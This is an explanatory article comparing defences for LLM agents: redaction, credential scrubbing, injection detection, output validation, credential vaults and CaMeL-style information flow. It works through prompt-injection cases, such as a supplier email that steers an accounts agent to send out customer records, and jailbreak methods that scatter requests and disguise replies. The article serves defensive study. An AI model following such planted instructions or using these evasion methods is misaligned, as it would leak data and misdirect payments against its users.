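# How secret scrubbing, prompt-injection detection and output validation divide the work of securing LLM agents

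## What an agent reads and writes, and where the four layers sit

A large language model (LLM) agent is a language model that works in a loop, calling tools such as a file reader or an email client and reading their results until it finishes a task. Companies use agents to write software, answer customers and handle invoices. These agents read text from strangers, handle passwords and personal details, and can send messages, delete files or make payments. SC Media reported that the 2026 list of LLM application risks from OWASP, a non-profit that publishes security guidance, ranks prompt injection first. Prompt injection is text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions. Disclosure of sensitive information is second, and third is excessive agency, which roughly means giving a system more power to act than its task needs.

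Developers commonly place four protective checks, or layers, around an agent. Redaction removes personal data, scrubbing removes credentials such as passwords, an injection detector looks for planted instructions, and output validation checks what the model produces. Some security engineers want separate layers, some want a single combined layer, and others consider all four less important than designs that keep secrets and authority away from the model. Much of their disagreement depends on which text passes where, and when.

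### The agent loop

*Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) describes the loop inside Codex, OpenAI's coding agent. The model only produces text, and an ordinary program around it, which Bolin calls the harness, does everything else. The harness puts the user's request, standing instructions and a list of available tools into a prompt and sends it to the model. The model returns either a final reply or a tool call, which is a structured request to run a function. If it returns a tool call, the harness runs the function, appends the result (the tool output) to the prompt and queries the model again. This repeats until the model returns a final reply. A single request can lead to hundreds of tool calls.

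A model's context is all the text it reads before a step, and it keeps growing. Codex sends the whole history to the model's provider with every query, partly so that OpenAI doesn't have to store anything for customers who forbid it. If a tool returns a password at the second step, Codex therefore sends that password with every later query until it condenses the history to save space.

Suppose a small company runs an accounts agent. A clerk asks it to refund a customer and types in the customer's name and bank account number. The agent needs the address of the payment system, so the model calls a file-reading tool. The tool returns a configuration file containing the address and an API key, which lets anyone who has it use the payment system. Next the model opens an email from the supplier of the returned goods. One sentence in the email is an instruction to the agent to send the company's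 customer records to an outside address. The model may carry on with the refund, or it may write a tool call that emails the records out, and the clerk could get the same final reply either way.

The API key and the bank details are both sensitive. The key is a credential that grants access, so anyone who copies it can act as the company until somebody cancels it. The bank details are personal data, which identifies a person and can include things the company can't replace after a leak, such as a customer's name. The agent may need that name to write to the customer, but the model doesn't need to read the key, because the program could attach it to requests. Keys also tend to be easier to spot because many have a fixed prefix and length, while a name can look like any other word.

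### One stream of text

A model may obey a sentence in a supplier's email because of how its context reaches it. *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion* (Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell, 2026) describes everything a model sees as one continuous stream of tokens, the word fragments in which it reads and writes. That stream contains system instructions, the user's questions, retrieved documents and the model's own earlier reasoning. Developers mark the parts with role tags, which label a passage as coming from the user, a tool or another source, and they train models to give some roles more authority than others. Models are supposed to treat tool output as information and never follow instructions in it.

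Ye and colleagues tested how much the tags affect which role a model assigns to text. They trained a probe, a small classifier that reads a model's internal activity, to estimate the role the model assigns to each token. The training text was identical under every tag, so the probe could learn only the effect of the tags. They then ran it on a conversation about gardening in gpt-oss-20b, an OpenAI model with public weights. Passages of the model's own reasoning scored 85% as reasoning under the correct tags, 83% with no tags, and 85% when the researchers labelled the entire conversation as user text. This was only one conversation, but the pattern held in other models. Attacks also succeeded more often when the probe showed more confusion about roles. Across 1,000 attempts to make an agent send data out, the success rate rose from 2% at the lowest level of confusion to 70% at the highest.

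SQL injection is a similar problem that developers have largely solved. An attacker types text into a web form, and the database runs it as a command. Parameterised queries prevent this by sending the command and the user's text to the database separately, so that the database never runs the text. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, published in December 2025, David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argued that language models can't separate commands from other text in this way, because a model only predicts the next token from the text so far. David C thinks it quite possible that nobody will ever fully fix prompt injection the way developers fixed SQL injection.

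Researchers have tried to build a separation between instructions and data into the model. Standard models give a token the same embedding, the list of numbers that represents it, whether it belongs to an instruction or to data. *ASIDE* (2025) proposes a different embedding for data. This assumes the system knows beforehand which text is instructions and which is data. It could, for instance, label every external file as data. In ordinary agents, however, tool output typically enters the context with no explicit mark of how far to trust it, according to Chu (2026) in *A Systematic Survey of Security Threats and Defenses in LLM-Based AI Agents*.

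The glossary of NIST, the US standards institute, defines *prompt injection* as an attack that exploits this mixing of untrusted input with a prompt written by a more trusted party. The injection is direct when the attacker types the request, and indirect when the injected text arrives in content that the agent reads during its task, as with the supplier's email. An indirect injection requires no access to the agent. David C gives the example of a job applicant who hides a line in a CV telling the recruiter's model to approve it. *The Landscape of Prompt Injection Threats in LLM Agents* (Wang, Li and colleagues, 2026) adds a supply-chain form, in which the attacker plants the text in a reference database or in training data. The paper traces all these attacks to one cause, a lack of isolation between inputs that deserve different levels of trust.

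### Where each layer can run

Redaction removes or replaces personal data before the model reads it. LangChain's *Guardrails*, a documentation page for a popular agent toolkit, lists four ways to handle personal data once it is detected. The program can replace it with a label, mask all but the last few digits, substitute a code that is always the same for the same value, or stop with an error. A label such as [EMAIL_1] is called a placeholder. Some systems instead use a surrogate, which is a realistic fake value in the same format. Credential scrubbing removes or replaces keys, passwords and tokens before the text reaches the model or any other destination.

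An injection detector is a classifier or model that scores text for planted instructions before the agent reads it. Output validation is any check on the model's reply or proposed tool call before it takes effect, from a format check to an LLM judge, which is a second language model that evaluates the output. Microsoft's Agent Control Specification, an open standard from June 2026, gives the example of a rule that prevents an email agent from writing to outsiders. The rule checks the recipient in each proposed tool call and blocks any external address. On the accounts agent, it would stop the customer records from being emailed out even if the model had followed the instruction in the supplier's sentence.

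Microsoft's standard defines eight points at which a check can run, including the start and end of a session. The points that matter for the four layers are these:

| Point on the loop | What passes there in the accounts example | Layers that can run there |
|---|---|---|
| User request | Customer's name and bank account number | Redaction, credential scrubbing, injection detection |
| Tool output, before the model reads it | Configuration file with the API key; supplier's email | Redaction, credential scrubbing, injection detection |
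| Tool call, before the program runs it | Recipient and text of an outgoing email | Output validation, credential scrubbing |
| Message to another agent | Refund details for a second agent that makes payments | All four |
| Memory | Notes that the agent keeps for later sessions | Redaction and scrubbing on writing; injection detection on reading back |
| Logs | A copy of nearly everything above | Masking of personal data, credential scrubbing |
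| Final reply | Confirmation to the clerk, perhaps with account details | Output validation, credential scrubbing |

The rows that no user sees are easy to forget. *AgentLeak* (El Yagoubi, Badu-Marfo and Al Mallah, 2026) looks at healthcare systems in which several agents share the work. In one case, a scheduling agent returned a clean appointment confirmation that would have passed any check on the final reply, but it had sent the patient's complete medical record to a second agent. The paper counts seven channels through which data can escape, including the files an agent leaves behind. In its tests, messages between agents leaked more often than final replies did.

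Chu describes how a document from a routine web search can plant text in an agent's long-term memory and influence an unrelated session weeks later. Detailed logs help developers detect attacks, but they also store sensitive text. David C advises developers to record enough to spot suspicious activity, potentially including the model's full input and output as well as its tool use. A log like that from the accounts agent would contain the API key. LiteLLM's *PII, PHI Masking*, documentation for a program that relays requests to models, describes a mode for this situation that masks personal data only in the log and leaves the request to the model and the reply unchanged.

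Products differ in where they put the same layer. LangChain's redaction is on by default for the user's messages and off for tool results and the model's own messages. Its built-in types cover email addresses, credit card numbers and a few kinds of network address, so the customer's name and bank account number would get through unless the developer wrote extra detectors. LangChain also shows how to catch API keys by giving the same component a pattern for them. Red Hat lists filters for secrets and personal data among the checks on output, which run after the model has read both. TrueFoundry, which sells a gateway for agent traffic, suggests removing secrets and personal data from tool results and running injection detection on everything that enters the model. OpenAI's guardrails library runs injection detection before and after each tool call but checks for personal data only at the agent's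 outer edges. These differences support the argument for separate layers, since each layer seems to have its own natural place in the loop.

Tool results need the closest checking because they can contain sensitive data that nobody typed. In Strathweb's *PII guardrails for .NET applications* (2026), a developer's walkthrough, an agent looks up a customer whose record contains an email address, a phone number and a social security number. The program replaces all three with placeholders before the model sees the record, and the model still writes a usable summary. If the program checked only after the model replied, the model would already have read the real values.

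### "Input" and "output"

Much of the confusion about placement comes from the words "input" and "output". They are clear enough in a chatbot, but in an agent, a tool's output is the model's next input, and the model's output may be the input to a tool. Even the end product can be ambiguous. Bolin notes that a coding agent's main output is often the code it changes on the user's machine, with the closing message as little more than a signal that it has finished.

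According to OpenAI's *Guardrails and human review*, part of the documentation for its agent toolkit, an "input guardrail" runs only for the first agent in a chain, and an "output guardrail" only for the agent that writes the final reply. Tool checks run only on the function tools to which the developer has attached them. A company that bought "input and output protection" for its accounts agent could therefore have a detector that checks the clerk's request but not the supplier's email. Microsoft partly avoids this problem in Foundry, its platform for building agents, by naming four points where checks can run: user input, tool call, tool response and output. But the two tool points are scanned only if the developer sets up controls there.

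### What the layers protect against

Three things can go wrong in the accounts example, and a layer that prevents one may not prevent the others. The first is disclosure to the provider, which happens even without an attacker, because the company that runs the model receives the bank account number and the API key as part of the context. The second is disclosure to an attacker, which happens if the agent emails the customer records to the outside address. The third is unauthorised action. If the supplier's email had told the agent to change the account into which the company pays its invoices, money would have gone to the wrong account without any secret being disclosed, and redaction and scrubbing would have had nothing to remove.

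Data hidden from the model provider can still reach an attacker. LangChain's *piiRedactionMiddleware*, now deprecated, replaced a social security number with a placeholder before the text went to the model. If the model then used the placeholder in a tool call, the function put the real number back so that the tool would work. LangChain described the benefit as "model provider isolation only" and listed the places where the data might remain, including saved state, logs, tool calls and the final reply. If the accounts agent used this function, a model that obeyed the supplier's email could write a message containing only the placeholder for the bank account, and the function would restore the real number before the message was sent. The attacker would then receive a number that the provider had never seen.

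El Yagoubi and colleagues also distinguish exposure, leakage and harm by how far the data has spread. The API key in the agent's context is internal exposure, which creates risk but may be necessary for the task. If the agent copies the key into a log where policy forbids it, that is leakage. Harm begins when an unauthorized person reads the log or uses the key. Their benchmark uses leakage as a stand-in for harm, so it measures policy violations rather than actual damage.

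### Two error rates

Every layer that has to recognise something makes two kinds of mistake. The miss rate is the share of harmful items it lets through, and the false-positive rate is the share of harmless items it flags. For example, a detector might check ten emails, four of which contain planted instructions. If it flags three of those four and one ordinary payment reminder, its miss rate is 25% (one in four) and its false-positive rate is about 17% (one in six). It is right about eight of the ten emails, but you can't work out either rate from that 80% accuracy alone.

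Injections are rarer in real mailboxes. If one email in a thousand carried an injection, the same detector would flag about 167 harmless emails for every thousand it read and would probably catch the injected one. The loop adds to the false alarms because an agent may read dozens of tool outputs in one task. If the false-positive rate were only 2% per output and errors were independent, a task with 50 outputs would have a 64% chance of at least one false alarm.

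The miss rate also depends on what counts as an item. A redactor that finds nine of the ten account numbers in a file misses 10% of the numbers, but counted per file it has failed, because a real account number still reaches the model.

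## The case for separate layers and the case for a combined one

The case for separate layers starts with how different their targets are: account numbers, API keys, planted instructions and payments. A tool that is good at finding one of these isn't necessarily good at finding the others.

The three layers also use different methods. Simple pattern matching finds many API keys, but redacting names in running text usually requires a model trained to label them. Detecting an injection requires judging what a sentence would make the agent do. Output validation can often be done with a few lines of ordinary code, such as a check that compares a refund with the original purchase.

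Mistakes also differ in how much harm they do. The company can cancel a leaked API key, but it can't change a customer's leaked name. A missed injection does no harm if the model ignores it, whereas the company loses money if the validator misses a bad payment. False alarms vary as much. A redactor that flags too much can leave a letter addressed to a placeholder, while a detector that flags too much can drop a supplier's email and stall the refund. The accounts agent seldom needs to read a long random string, so a developer might set the scrubber to flag almost anything that looks random, but set the detector to flag less readily. *Secure agent inputs and outputs*, part of the guidance on building agents from Amazon's cloud division, AWS, recommends setting strictness by the likelihood and impact of each risk. It also warns that overly broad filters erode users' trust and push teams to weaken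 the filters or switch them off.

Red Hat recommends testing guardrails like code, with fixed prompts and contexts and an expected verdict for each. Developers rerun the tests whenever a prompt, model or rule changes. Testing is easier when each layer does one job. For example, a developer can run a credential scrubber on two hundred fake keys and count the ones it misses. If one model does all four jobs and an update makes its verdicts worse, the developer first has to find out which job got worse. Separate layers also allow different settings for user messages and replies. A sample in *Guardrails Configuration*, NVIDIA's documentation for its NeMo Guardrails toolkit, checks the user's message for names, email addresses and card numbers, but checks the reply only for names and email addresses.

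The table below shows whether each layer could detect each of seven failures of the accounts agent, assuming the developer runs every layer wherever it can run. "Yes" means only that the text the layer reads contains the evidence, and the layer may still miss it.

| Failure | Redaction | Credential scrubbing | Injection detector | Output validation |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| The model's provider receives the customer's bank account number | Yes | No | No | No, it runs too late |
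| The provider receives the API key from the configuration file | No | Yes | No | No, it runs too late |
| The model reads the planted instruction in the supplier's email | No | No | Yes | No, only an action that results |
| The agent emails customer records to an outside address | Partly, by hiding values in the records beforehand | Only keys in the records | Only the instruction behind it | Yes, from the recipient |
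| The agent changes the account into which the company pays its invoices | No | No | Only the instruction behind it | Yes, if a rule covers payment details |
| The program copies the API key into a log | No | Yes | No | No |
| The agent refunds the wrong customer by mistake | No | No | No | Yes, if a check compares the refund with the order |

No column covers every row, and dropping any one column leaves at least one failure undetected. The mistaken refund involves no attacker and no secret, so three of the four layers have nothing to detect. The two API key failures occur only because the model reads the key. A credential vault would prevent this by having a trusted component add the key to a request after the model has chosen the action.

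Chu makes a more general version of this argument, dividing an agent into seven parts, including memory, tool execution and coordination between agents, and offering a proof that a control in one part can't detect an attack confined to another. Those parts aren't the four layers in the table, so the proof supports separating the layers only by analogy.

Ahmed, Saleem and colleagues (2026) ran a closer test in *A Layered Security Framework Against Prompt Injection in RAG-Based Chatbots*, using chatbots that answer from a store of documents. They point out that a filter on the user's message never reads the retrieved documents, and that a monitor on the reply can't keep an injection from reaching the model. Their three layers screen the user's message, give retrieved text less authority than the operator's instructions, and audit the reply. Across 5,080 harmless and malicious samples, the layers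 together cut the success rate of attacks from 71.4% to 11.3%, while the best single layer they compared left it at roughly 39%. However, the models date from 2024 or earlier and answered questions rather than calling tools, so these numbers are a poor guide to how current agents would perform.

### How published schemes divide the work

Most published guidance splits up the work somehow, but the lines fall in different places.

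The 2025 edition of OWASP's Top 10 for LLM applications divides the work by risk, with separate entries for prompt injection, disclosure and output handling. *LLM02:2025 Sensitive Information Disclosure* covers both personal data and security credentials. *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling* covers programs that pass the model's output to another system unchecked, for example by running a database command that the model wrote. It advises treating the model like any other user and validating whatever it sends. One of its scenarios falls under all three entries. An injection in a web page gets the model to collect sensitive content from the conversation, encode it and send it to the attacker's server, which succeeds because nothing checks the output.

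In the 2026 edition, output handling fell from fifth place to tenth, while excessive agency rose from sixth to third. Respan, a company that sells agent testing, says in its summary *OWASP LLM Top 10* (2026) that OWASP limits output handling to the unsafe use of output and assigns checks on what enters the model to prompt injection. A tool call that changes a supplier's bank details can be well formed, so it seems to fit better under excessive agency, which covers damaging actions regardless of why the model misbehaved. An output validation layer has to deal with both risks. OWASP lists risks rather than products, so three entries don't have to mean three pieces of software.

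AWS divides the work by direction. Injection checks go on everything the agent reads, including tool outputs, messages from other agents and its own memory. Checks for personal data and credentials go on everything it sends, including what it writes to memory and audit logs. AWS describes five levels of maturity:

- At level one, checks run only on the user's messages, if at all, and the developer relies on asking the model to keep sensitive things to itself.
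- Level two has an injection detector and basic filters for personal data, mostly on what users type and what they get back.
- At level three, every input has a control and every outgoing path has a filter.
- At level four, developers periodically tune the filters against labelled samples of real traffic.
- At level five, tuning runs on a schedule, with false positives and misses as the main measures.

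An accounts agent that checks the clerk's request with an excellent detector but leaves the supplier's email unchecked would still be at level one or two.

NVIDIA's *Guardrail Types* divides the checks in NeMo Guardrails by stage into five kinds: those on the user's input, retrieved documents, the course of the conversation, tool calls and their results, and the reply. It lists masking personal data under input and removing sensitive data under output, so the same kind of protection appears at two stages.

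Meta divides LlamaFirewall, its open-source toolkit for agents, by type of threat. Meta's *LlamaFirewall Architecture* describes a small classifier, PromptGuard 2, that looks for injections in user input and untrusted content. AlignmentCheck, an LLM judge, checks the agent's reasoning against what the user wanted. CodeShield scans the code that an agent writes. To catch secrets, developers configure a general scanner with their own patterns, and no component deals specifically with personal data. When Meta released the toolkit, Chennabasappa, Nikolaidis and colleagues (2025) called AlignmentCheck "still experimental" in *LlamaFirewall*, although Meta was already using the toolkit in production.

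An example in Meta's *LlamaFirewall Workflow and Detection Components* is a good argument for separate layers. A coding agent copies an insecure database query from a popular, well-meant post. The post contains no injection, so neither PromptGuard nor a better injection detector would flag it, but CodeShield catches the problem in the agent's code.

The schemes differ most in how they handle credentials. OWASP, AWS and Red Hat group them with personal data, which makes sense if the concern is that a reply will leak them. Meta leaves them to custom patterns. LLM Guard, a Python toolkit described in VIPS's *LLM Guard*, has separate scanners for personal data, secrets and injections, although a developer can run all three with a single function call. The schemes also differ on actions that don't match the user's request. Meta treats a mismatch mainly as a sign that an injection has worked, while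 OWASP's "excessive agency" category also covers an agent that misunderstood the request.

### The argument from context

One argument for a combined layer is that a layer that reads only the digits of a bank account number can't tell a leak from a legitimate payment. The agent may send the number to the payment system to refund the customer, but sending the same number to a stranger is a leak. Infosecurity Magazine's *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* gives OWASP's 2026 definition of disclosure as the exposure of confidential data through an unauthorised channel. A pattern that matches account numbers doesn't check the channel, and there are many to check. Respan mentions tool-call arguments, reasoning traces, logs and even the timing of responses.

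The same problem arises with instructions. Suppose the supplier's email asks the reader to fill in a return form and send it to the warehouse. That request is part of the task if the clerk told the agent to do whatever the supplier needs for the return, but the agent shouldn't act on it if the clerk asked only for a summary. A detector that reads only the email can't distinguish the two cases. Likewise, a change to a supplier's bank details is routine if the finance manager asked for it and probably fraud if the only request came by email.

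A layer that reads the whole context could work out who asked for what, where each piece of text came from and where it is going, and could detect harm that builds up over several steps. The accounts agent might have permission to read customer records, save a summary in a folder and share that folder with a supplier, and by doing all three in a row it could expose customer data. Chu describes attacks like this, in which each action is authorised but the combination is harmful, and argues that detectors that each watch only one part of the agent can miss attacks that cross between parts. Chu's survey supports separate controls, but this argument is also a reason for those controls to share what they find.

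Ahmed and colleagues criticise NeMo Guardrails and Llama Guard, an earlier safety classifier, for treating checks on input and output as independent. In the system they built, the layer that screens the user's message passes any warning to the layer that audits the reply. This keeps the layers separate but gives the last one more information.

### Classifiers that read prompt and reply together

The best evidence for a combined layer comes from a different problem, jailbreaks, which are prompts that get a model to help with something it would normally refuse. Anthropic's *Constitutional Classifiers* (2025) protected a chatbot against jailbreaks with two classifiers, one for the prompt and one for the reply. The pair raised the refusal rate by 0.38% in a sample of real conversations and required 23.7% more computing.

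*Constitutional Classifiers++* (Cunningham, Wei and colleagues, 2026) reports two weaknesses in this arrangement. Attackers could get a request past the prompt classifier by scattering it through a longer, harmless-looking text. They could also have the model disguise its reply so that it looked innocent to anyone who hadn't read the prompt. The drawback for attackers is that these methods make the model worse at its work. Claude Opus 4's accuracy on a set of hard science questions fell from 74.2% to 32.3% under one attack that scattered the request and disguised the reply, and to 49% under another.

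The researchers replaced the pair with a single exchange classifier, which checks the prompt and then reads the reply alongside it as the model writes. They asked red-teamers, people who attack a system to test it, to find a method for getting answers to eight questions about chemical, biological, radiological or nuclear weapons. A method counted as a high-risk vulnerability if more than five of the answers it got had at least half the detail an unprotected model would give. The team then built two systems that also read the whole exchange but use less compute.

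| System | High-risk vulnerabilities found | Rate per 1,000 queries | Computing cost relative to the pair | Real traffic refused |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Separate prompt and reply classifiers | 13 in 695,000 queries | 0.0187 | 100% | 0.073% |
| One exchange classifier | 2 in 226,000 | 0.0089 | 150% | 0.038% |
| Small exchange classifier that passes suspicious cases to a larger one | 5 in 569,000 | 0.0088 | 27.8% | 0.036% |
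| Probe of the model's internal activity, joined by an exchange classifier for suspicious cases | 1 in 198,000 | 0.0051 | 3.5% | 0.050% |

The single exchange classifier had about half the vulnerability rate of the pair, but that rate is based on only two vulnerabilities. At the pair's rate, red-teamers would have found about four in 226,000 queries, and they would find two or fewer by chance about one time in five. The two systems also differed in more than what their classifiers read. The exchange classifier was a larger model than the pair's reply classifier, which explains why it needed more compute and may explain some of the improvement. The systems also guarded different Claude models, though Cunningham and colleagues don't think this mattered much. All three systems that read the whole exchange did better than the pair, which makes a real advantage more likely, but the later two also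 used newer classifiers.

The system that uses the least compute weakens the case for a single layer, because it combines two kinds of classifier. The probe reads the internal activity of the model it protects, while the exchange classifier reads the text. On about 7,000 recorded jailbreak attempts, the scores of a probe and a text classifier agreed less than those of two text classifiers, and combining a probe with a text classifier worked better than using either alone. The design that performed best gave its classifiers the whole exchange but still used two methods to judge it.

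None of this work concerned agents' secrets. In these tests the attacker was the user, and instructions for making a weapon are dangerous whoever asks for them. The accounts agent has an honest user, and the attacker wrote one email among the many texts it reads. It also handles data that can be harmless in one message and a leak in another. Context probably matters more for this agent, but there is also far more of it to read than in a chatbot exchange, which can be a single prompt and reply.

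### How each side answers the other

Supporters of separate layers can accept the argument from context and still object to the timing. By the time any classifier reads the reply, the provider already has the bank account number and the API key, and flagging the reply can't undo that. A combined layer also has to read the key to decide whether it is leaking, which sends the key to one more place unless the layer runs on the company's own machines. If the layer is a language model, the instruction planted in the supplier's email may work on it too, because it also reads the email. Ahmed and colleagues mention an earlier defence in which a second model paraphrased each input and was itself open to injection.

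Supporters of a combined layer can reply that its verdicts can still be explained. Red Hat divides its guardrails by stage but also recommends a critic, a second model that checks a proposed answer or plan for policy violations, data exposure and unsafe actions together. The critic can label each decision with a risk and a type of reason, so developers can still count its mistakes by kind. Testing layers separately can also mislead. A redactor that finds every account number in a test file gets a perfect score, even if it would also remove the number from a message that needs it.

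Some of the disagreement is over what "combined" means. Amazon's Bedrock Guardrails is one product, but it contains several filters with their own confidence scores. AlignmentCheck is one component among several, yet it needs the user's goal as input. A developer could keep redaction and scrubbing as separate steps before the model reads anything, then have a judge with the full context check each proposed action. The evidence so far seems to support that mixture more than either pure design. Whether it would work well depends on four points on which the two cases differ.

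### What the two cases dispute

The two sides disagree first about how much each design interferes with the agent's task. A separate redactor removes values without checking whether the agent needs them, so supporters of a combined layer expect it to spoil more letters and cause more refunds to fail. Supporters of separation expect placeholders to be good enough for most tasks, and they can point out that a judge that wrongly stops payments also harms the company.

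The two sides also disagree about how reliable detection can be. A separate detector is worth having if it can recognise planted instructions from the text alone. If it also needs the user's request, it has to become more like a combined layer. That is an improvement only if a detector with the full context makes fewer mistakes, including when attackers adapt to it.

An output validation rule can easily block an email to an unknown address. It is much harder to write a rule that catches an email to an approved supplier that mentions another customer's details in an ordinary-looking sentence. The more harm comes from emails of the second kind, the stronger the case for a judge that knows the purpose of the email.

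Two layers that each miss one attack in ten will together miss one in a hundred only if their errors are independent, and an attacker who knows about both layers can write a single email to get past them.

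## The case for keeping credentials and authority away from the model

If one email can get past every filter, the damage depends on what the agent can do after reading it. Some security engineers therefore start by limiting the agent's powers. They would give the accounts agent no API key to leak and no way to send customer records to strangers, and they treat redaction, scrubbing and detection as useful extras. They argue that a language model can't reliably separate instructions from data, so no filter can guarantee that the model will ignore a planted instruction.

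### Structure instead of recognition

SQL injection is the usual comparison because developers tried both approaches on it. Early on, some tried to recognise bad input. A filter might reject any text containing an apostrophe, because an apostrophe ends a piece of text in SQL and can let whatever follows run as a command. But that filter also rejects a customer named O'Brien, and attackers found ways to do without the apostrophe. Parameterised queries keep the command separate from the user's text. The database treats both O'Brien's name and an attacker's command as plain characters in the name column, so it doesn't need a filter to tell them apart.

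*Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (Narisetty, Kore and colleagues, 2026) concludes from the history of earlier software attacks that "detection lost and structure won". Buffer overflows let an attacker's data spill into the part of memory that controls a program, and engineers contained them partly by making data impossible to execute. Cross-site scripting plants a script in a web page, and developers contained it by encoding users' text so that browsers display it instead of running it.

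Prompt injection has the same cause as SQL injection, but nobody has found an equivalent fix. A parser can use SQL's grammar to separate a command from a value, but English has no grammar that allows this. "Send the form to the warehouse" could be an order to the agent, a line that the clerk wants translated, or a record of what somebody told a driver last week. Models also learn in training to follow instructions wherever they appear. Narisetty and colleagues cite measurements in which neither prompting nor further training reliably gave models a usable separation between instructions and data.

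David C prefers to call a language model an "inherently confusable deputy". A confused deputy is a program that someone with less authority tricks into using its authority on their behalf. For example, a supplier who can't read a company's customer records might email the company's accounts agent, which can, and ask it to send them. Developers can fix an ordinary confused deputy but may never be able to fix a language model, so David C advises them to assume that a successful injection is as bad as giving the attacker direct access to the agent's tools. The main protection should then be deterministic safeguards, which are ordinary code that limits what the system can do whatever the model produces. If the remaining risk is unacceptable, the system may not be a good use for a language model.

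OpenAI has said that prompt injection is "unlikely to ever be fully 'solved'", according to Narisetty and colleagues. Simon Willison, the software developer who named prompt injection in 2022, worked out a rule with Baibhav Bista in an online exchange that David C quotes: when a model processes information from some party, its privileges should drop to those of that party. This is close to a much older rule from Biba's model of data integrity, under which a program that reads untrusted data drops to that data's level of trust and can't change anything above it.

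Willison and Bista's rule would make the accounts agent much less useful, because its job is to act on what strangers write. If applied strictly, the rule would let the agent read the supplier's email or issue the refund, but not both in one session.

All these statements concern guarantees. Narisetty and colleagues accept that some filters and some kinds of training hold ordinary attacks to low rates and are worth having as one layer. They worry about persistent attackers. They report adaptive tests of Claude Opus 4.5, an Anthropic model from late 2025, in coding environments. Attacks succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63.0% with a hundred. A supplier can easily send a hundred emails. If the attempts had been independent, at least one in a hundred would have succeeded more than 99% of the time, so some targets seem to have been much harder than others.

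### How a credential vault works

The accounts agent has to prove its identity to the payment system, but the model does nothing with the API key except pass it along. A credential vault makes that unnecessary. Kenney, Ahmadi and colleagues (2026), in *API Secrets Should Never Become Tokens in the LLM's Vocabulary*, describe one called Corvic Security Vault. For each outside service it stores a record called a connector, which holds the service's address, the key, and the place in a request where the key belongs. In the accounts example, a refund would work roughly like this:

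1. The program gives the model a list of connectors, such as "payments", without their keys.
2. The model writes a tool call that names the connector and gives the details of the refund.
3. The agent's code prepares the request. This code runs in a sandbox, a closed environment with limited access to anything outside it, and the key isn't in there either.
4. A trusted component outside the sandbox compares the request's destination with the address in the connector's record.
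5. If the two match, that component adds the key and sends the request on. A request to any other address goes out without the key.
6. The payment system's answer comes back to the model as tool output.

If the supplier's email tells the agent to reveal the API key, the model can't, because it doesn't have the key. Telling the agent to contact the attacker's server wouldn't expose the key either, because the vault attaches it only to requests for one destination.

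Kenney and colleagues divide a credential leak into five stages. First, someone puts a key into a prompt, a file or a tool definition. Conversation history, logs and memory then copy it. An injection or an ordinary model error leads to its disclosure or misuse, and the key's permissions determine how much harm follows. Finally, a long-lived key keeps working outside the session where it leaked. A vault can eliminate the first two stages, because a key that never enters the context can't be copied from it. The vault doesn't limit what the key permits, so an agent that has never read a key can still use a connector to delete something.

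The researchers work for Corvic AI, the company that built the vault. On 27 September 2026 they ran two experiments on the live product. In each, they gave code in the sandbox a single connector and a fixed set of probes, and they wrote down the expected result of each probe beforehand. The probes covered seven areas, including files, environment variables and the handling of requests to other sites.

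In the GitHub experiment, code that contained no credential fetched the details of the logged-in user. This control was important because a sandbox with no network connection would also have passed every leak test. Across the two experiments, the probes found nothing resembling a credential in 20 environment variables or at 12 common file locations. The key didn't appear in responses from three echo services, which return a copy of whatever request they receive. A request to OpenAI's API failed for lack of authentication in both experiments, so the vault hadn't attached another service's key to it. Requests to the addresses where cloud machines get their own credentials timed out.

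All 16 probes gave the expected result, but the connector for FRED, an economic data service run by the Federal Reserve Bank of St. Louis, didn't work. FRED requires its key in the query part of the web address, and the connector was configured to send it in a header, so FRED rejected the request. The researchers scored this separately as a functional failure because nothing leaked. A developer in a hurry might respond to such a failure by pasting the key into the code.

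The 16 passes show that the basic mechanism worked in these tests, but they are weak evidence that it works reliably. Even with a random sample, 16 successes in a row would be compatible with a true failure rate of about 17%, and Kenney and colleagues, who built the mechanism, chose these probes by hand. They didn't test redirects, a connected service that an attacker had taken over, or whether an injection could make a model misuse a working connector. They name that last test as the most valuable next experiment.

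They also scored eight threats before and after adding the vault by rating likelihood and impact from 1 to 5 and multiplying the two. The scores are their own judgments, not measurements.

| Threat | Score before | Score with the vault |
|---|---|---|
| User pastes a secret into the prompt | 25 | 4 |
| Indirect prompt injection | 25 | 12 |
| Credential sent to the wrong destination | 20 | 4 |
| Agent's code finds a credential in its environment | 20 | 4 |
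| Connector with more permissions than it needs | 20 | 15 |
| Attacker reuses a long-lived token | 20 | 8 |
| Leak through logs or error messages | 16 | 8 |
| Badly configured connector | 9 | 6 |

The builders themselves say that injection remains a substantial risk and that the problem of excessive permissions hardly improves. A key that can issue refunds of any size can still do so when it is stored in a vault. The score for pasted secrets looks too generous, because nothing in the six steps above stops a clerk from pasting a key into the chat. Kenney and colleagues recommend detecting and blocking such keys separately, which a credential scrubber does.

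### Following a value to the tool call

An agent with a safely stored key can still pay the wrong person. Information-flow designs address this by labeling each value with where it came from and who may receive it, then checking those labels when the value reaches a tool call. The two main designs are CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues at Google and ETH Zurich published in 2025, and FIDES, from researchers at Microsoft.

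CaMeL develops an earlier idea of Willison's, which was to use two models, one that can act and one that reads untrusted text. Suppose the clerk asks the accounts agent to refund the customer on a particular order by the amount that the supplier agreed in its last email. In a design like CaMeL, the amount would travel as follows:

| Step | What happens | Labels |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | A planning model reads the clerk's request and writes a short program. It never reads the email. | The program is trusted, because it comes only from the clerk's request |
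| 2 | The program fetches the supplier's email. | Source: supplier |
| 3 | A second model, which has no tools, reads the email and returns the number 84. | Source: supplier, carried over from the email |
| 4 | The program looks up the customer's bank account number. | Source: company records. May go to: payment system |
| 5 | The program proposes a refund of $84 to that account, and an interpreter checks both values against the company's policy. | Account: allowed, because it comes from company records. Amount: allowed up to the price on the order |
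| 6 | The refund goes through. | |

The planted sentence in the email, which asks for the customer records, reaches only the second model. That model can't call a tool, and the program has no step that sends records anywhere. At worst, the model can return a wrong amount, which the policy caps at the price of the order. If the program had taken the account number from the email instead, the interpreter would have blocked the payment because of the number's source. It would also block an email to the supplier containing the customer's account number, since that number may go only to the payment system.

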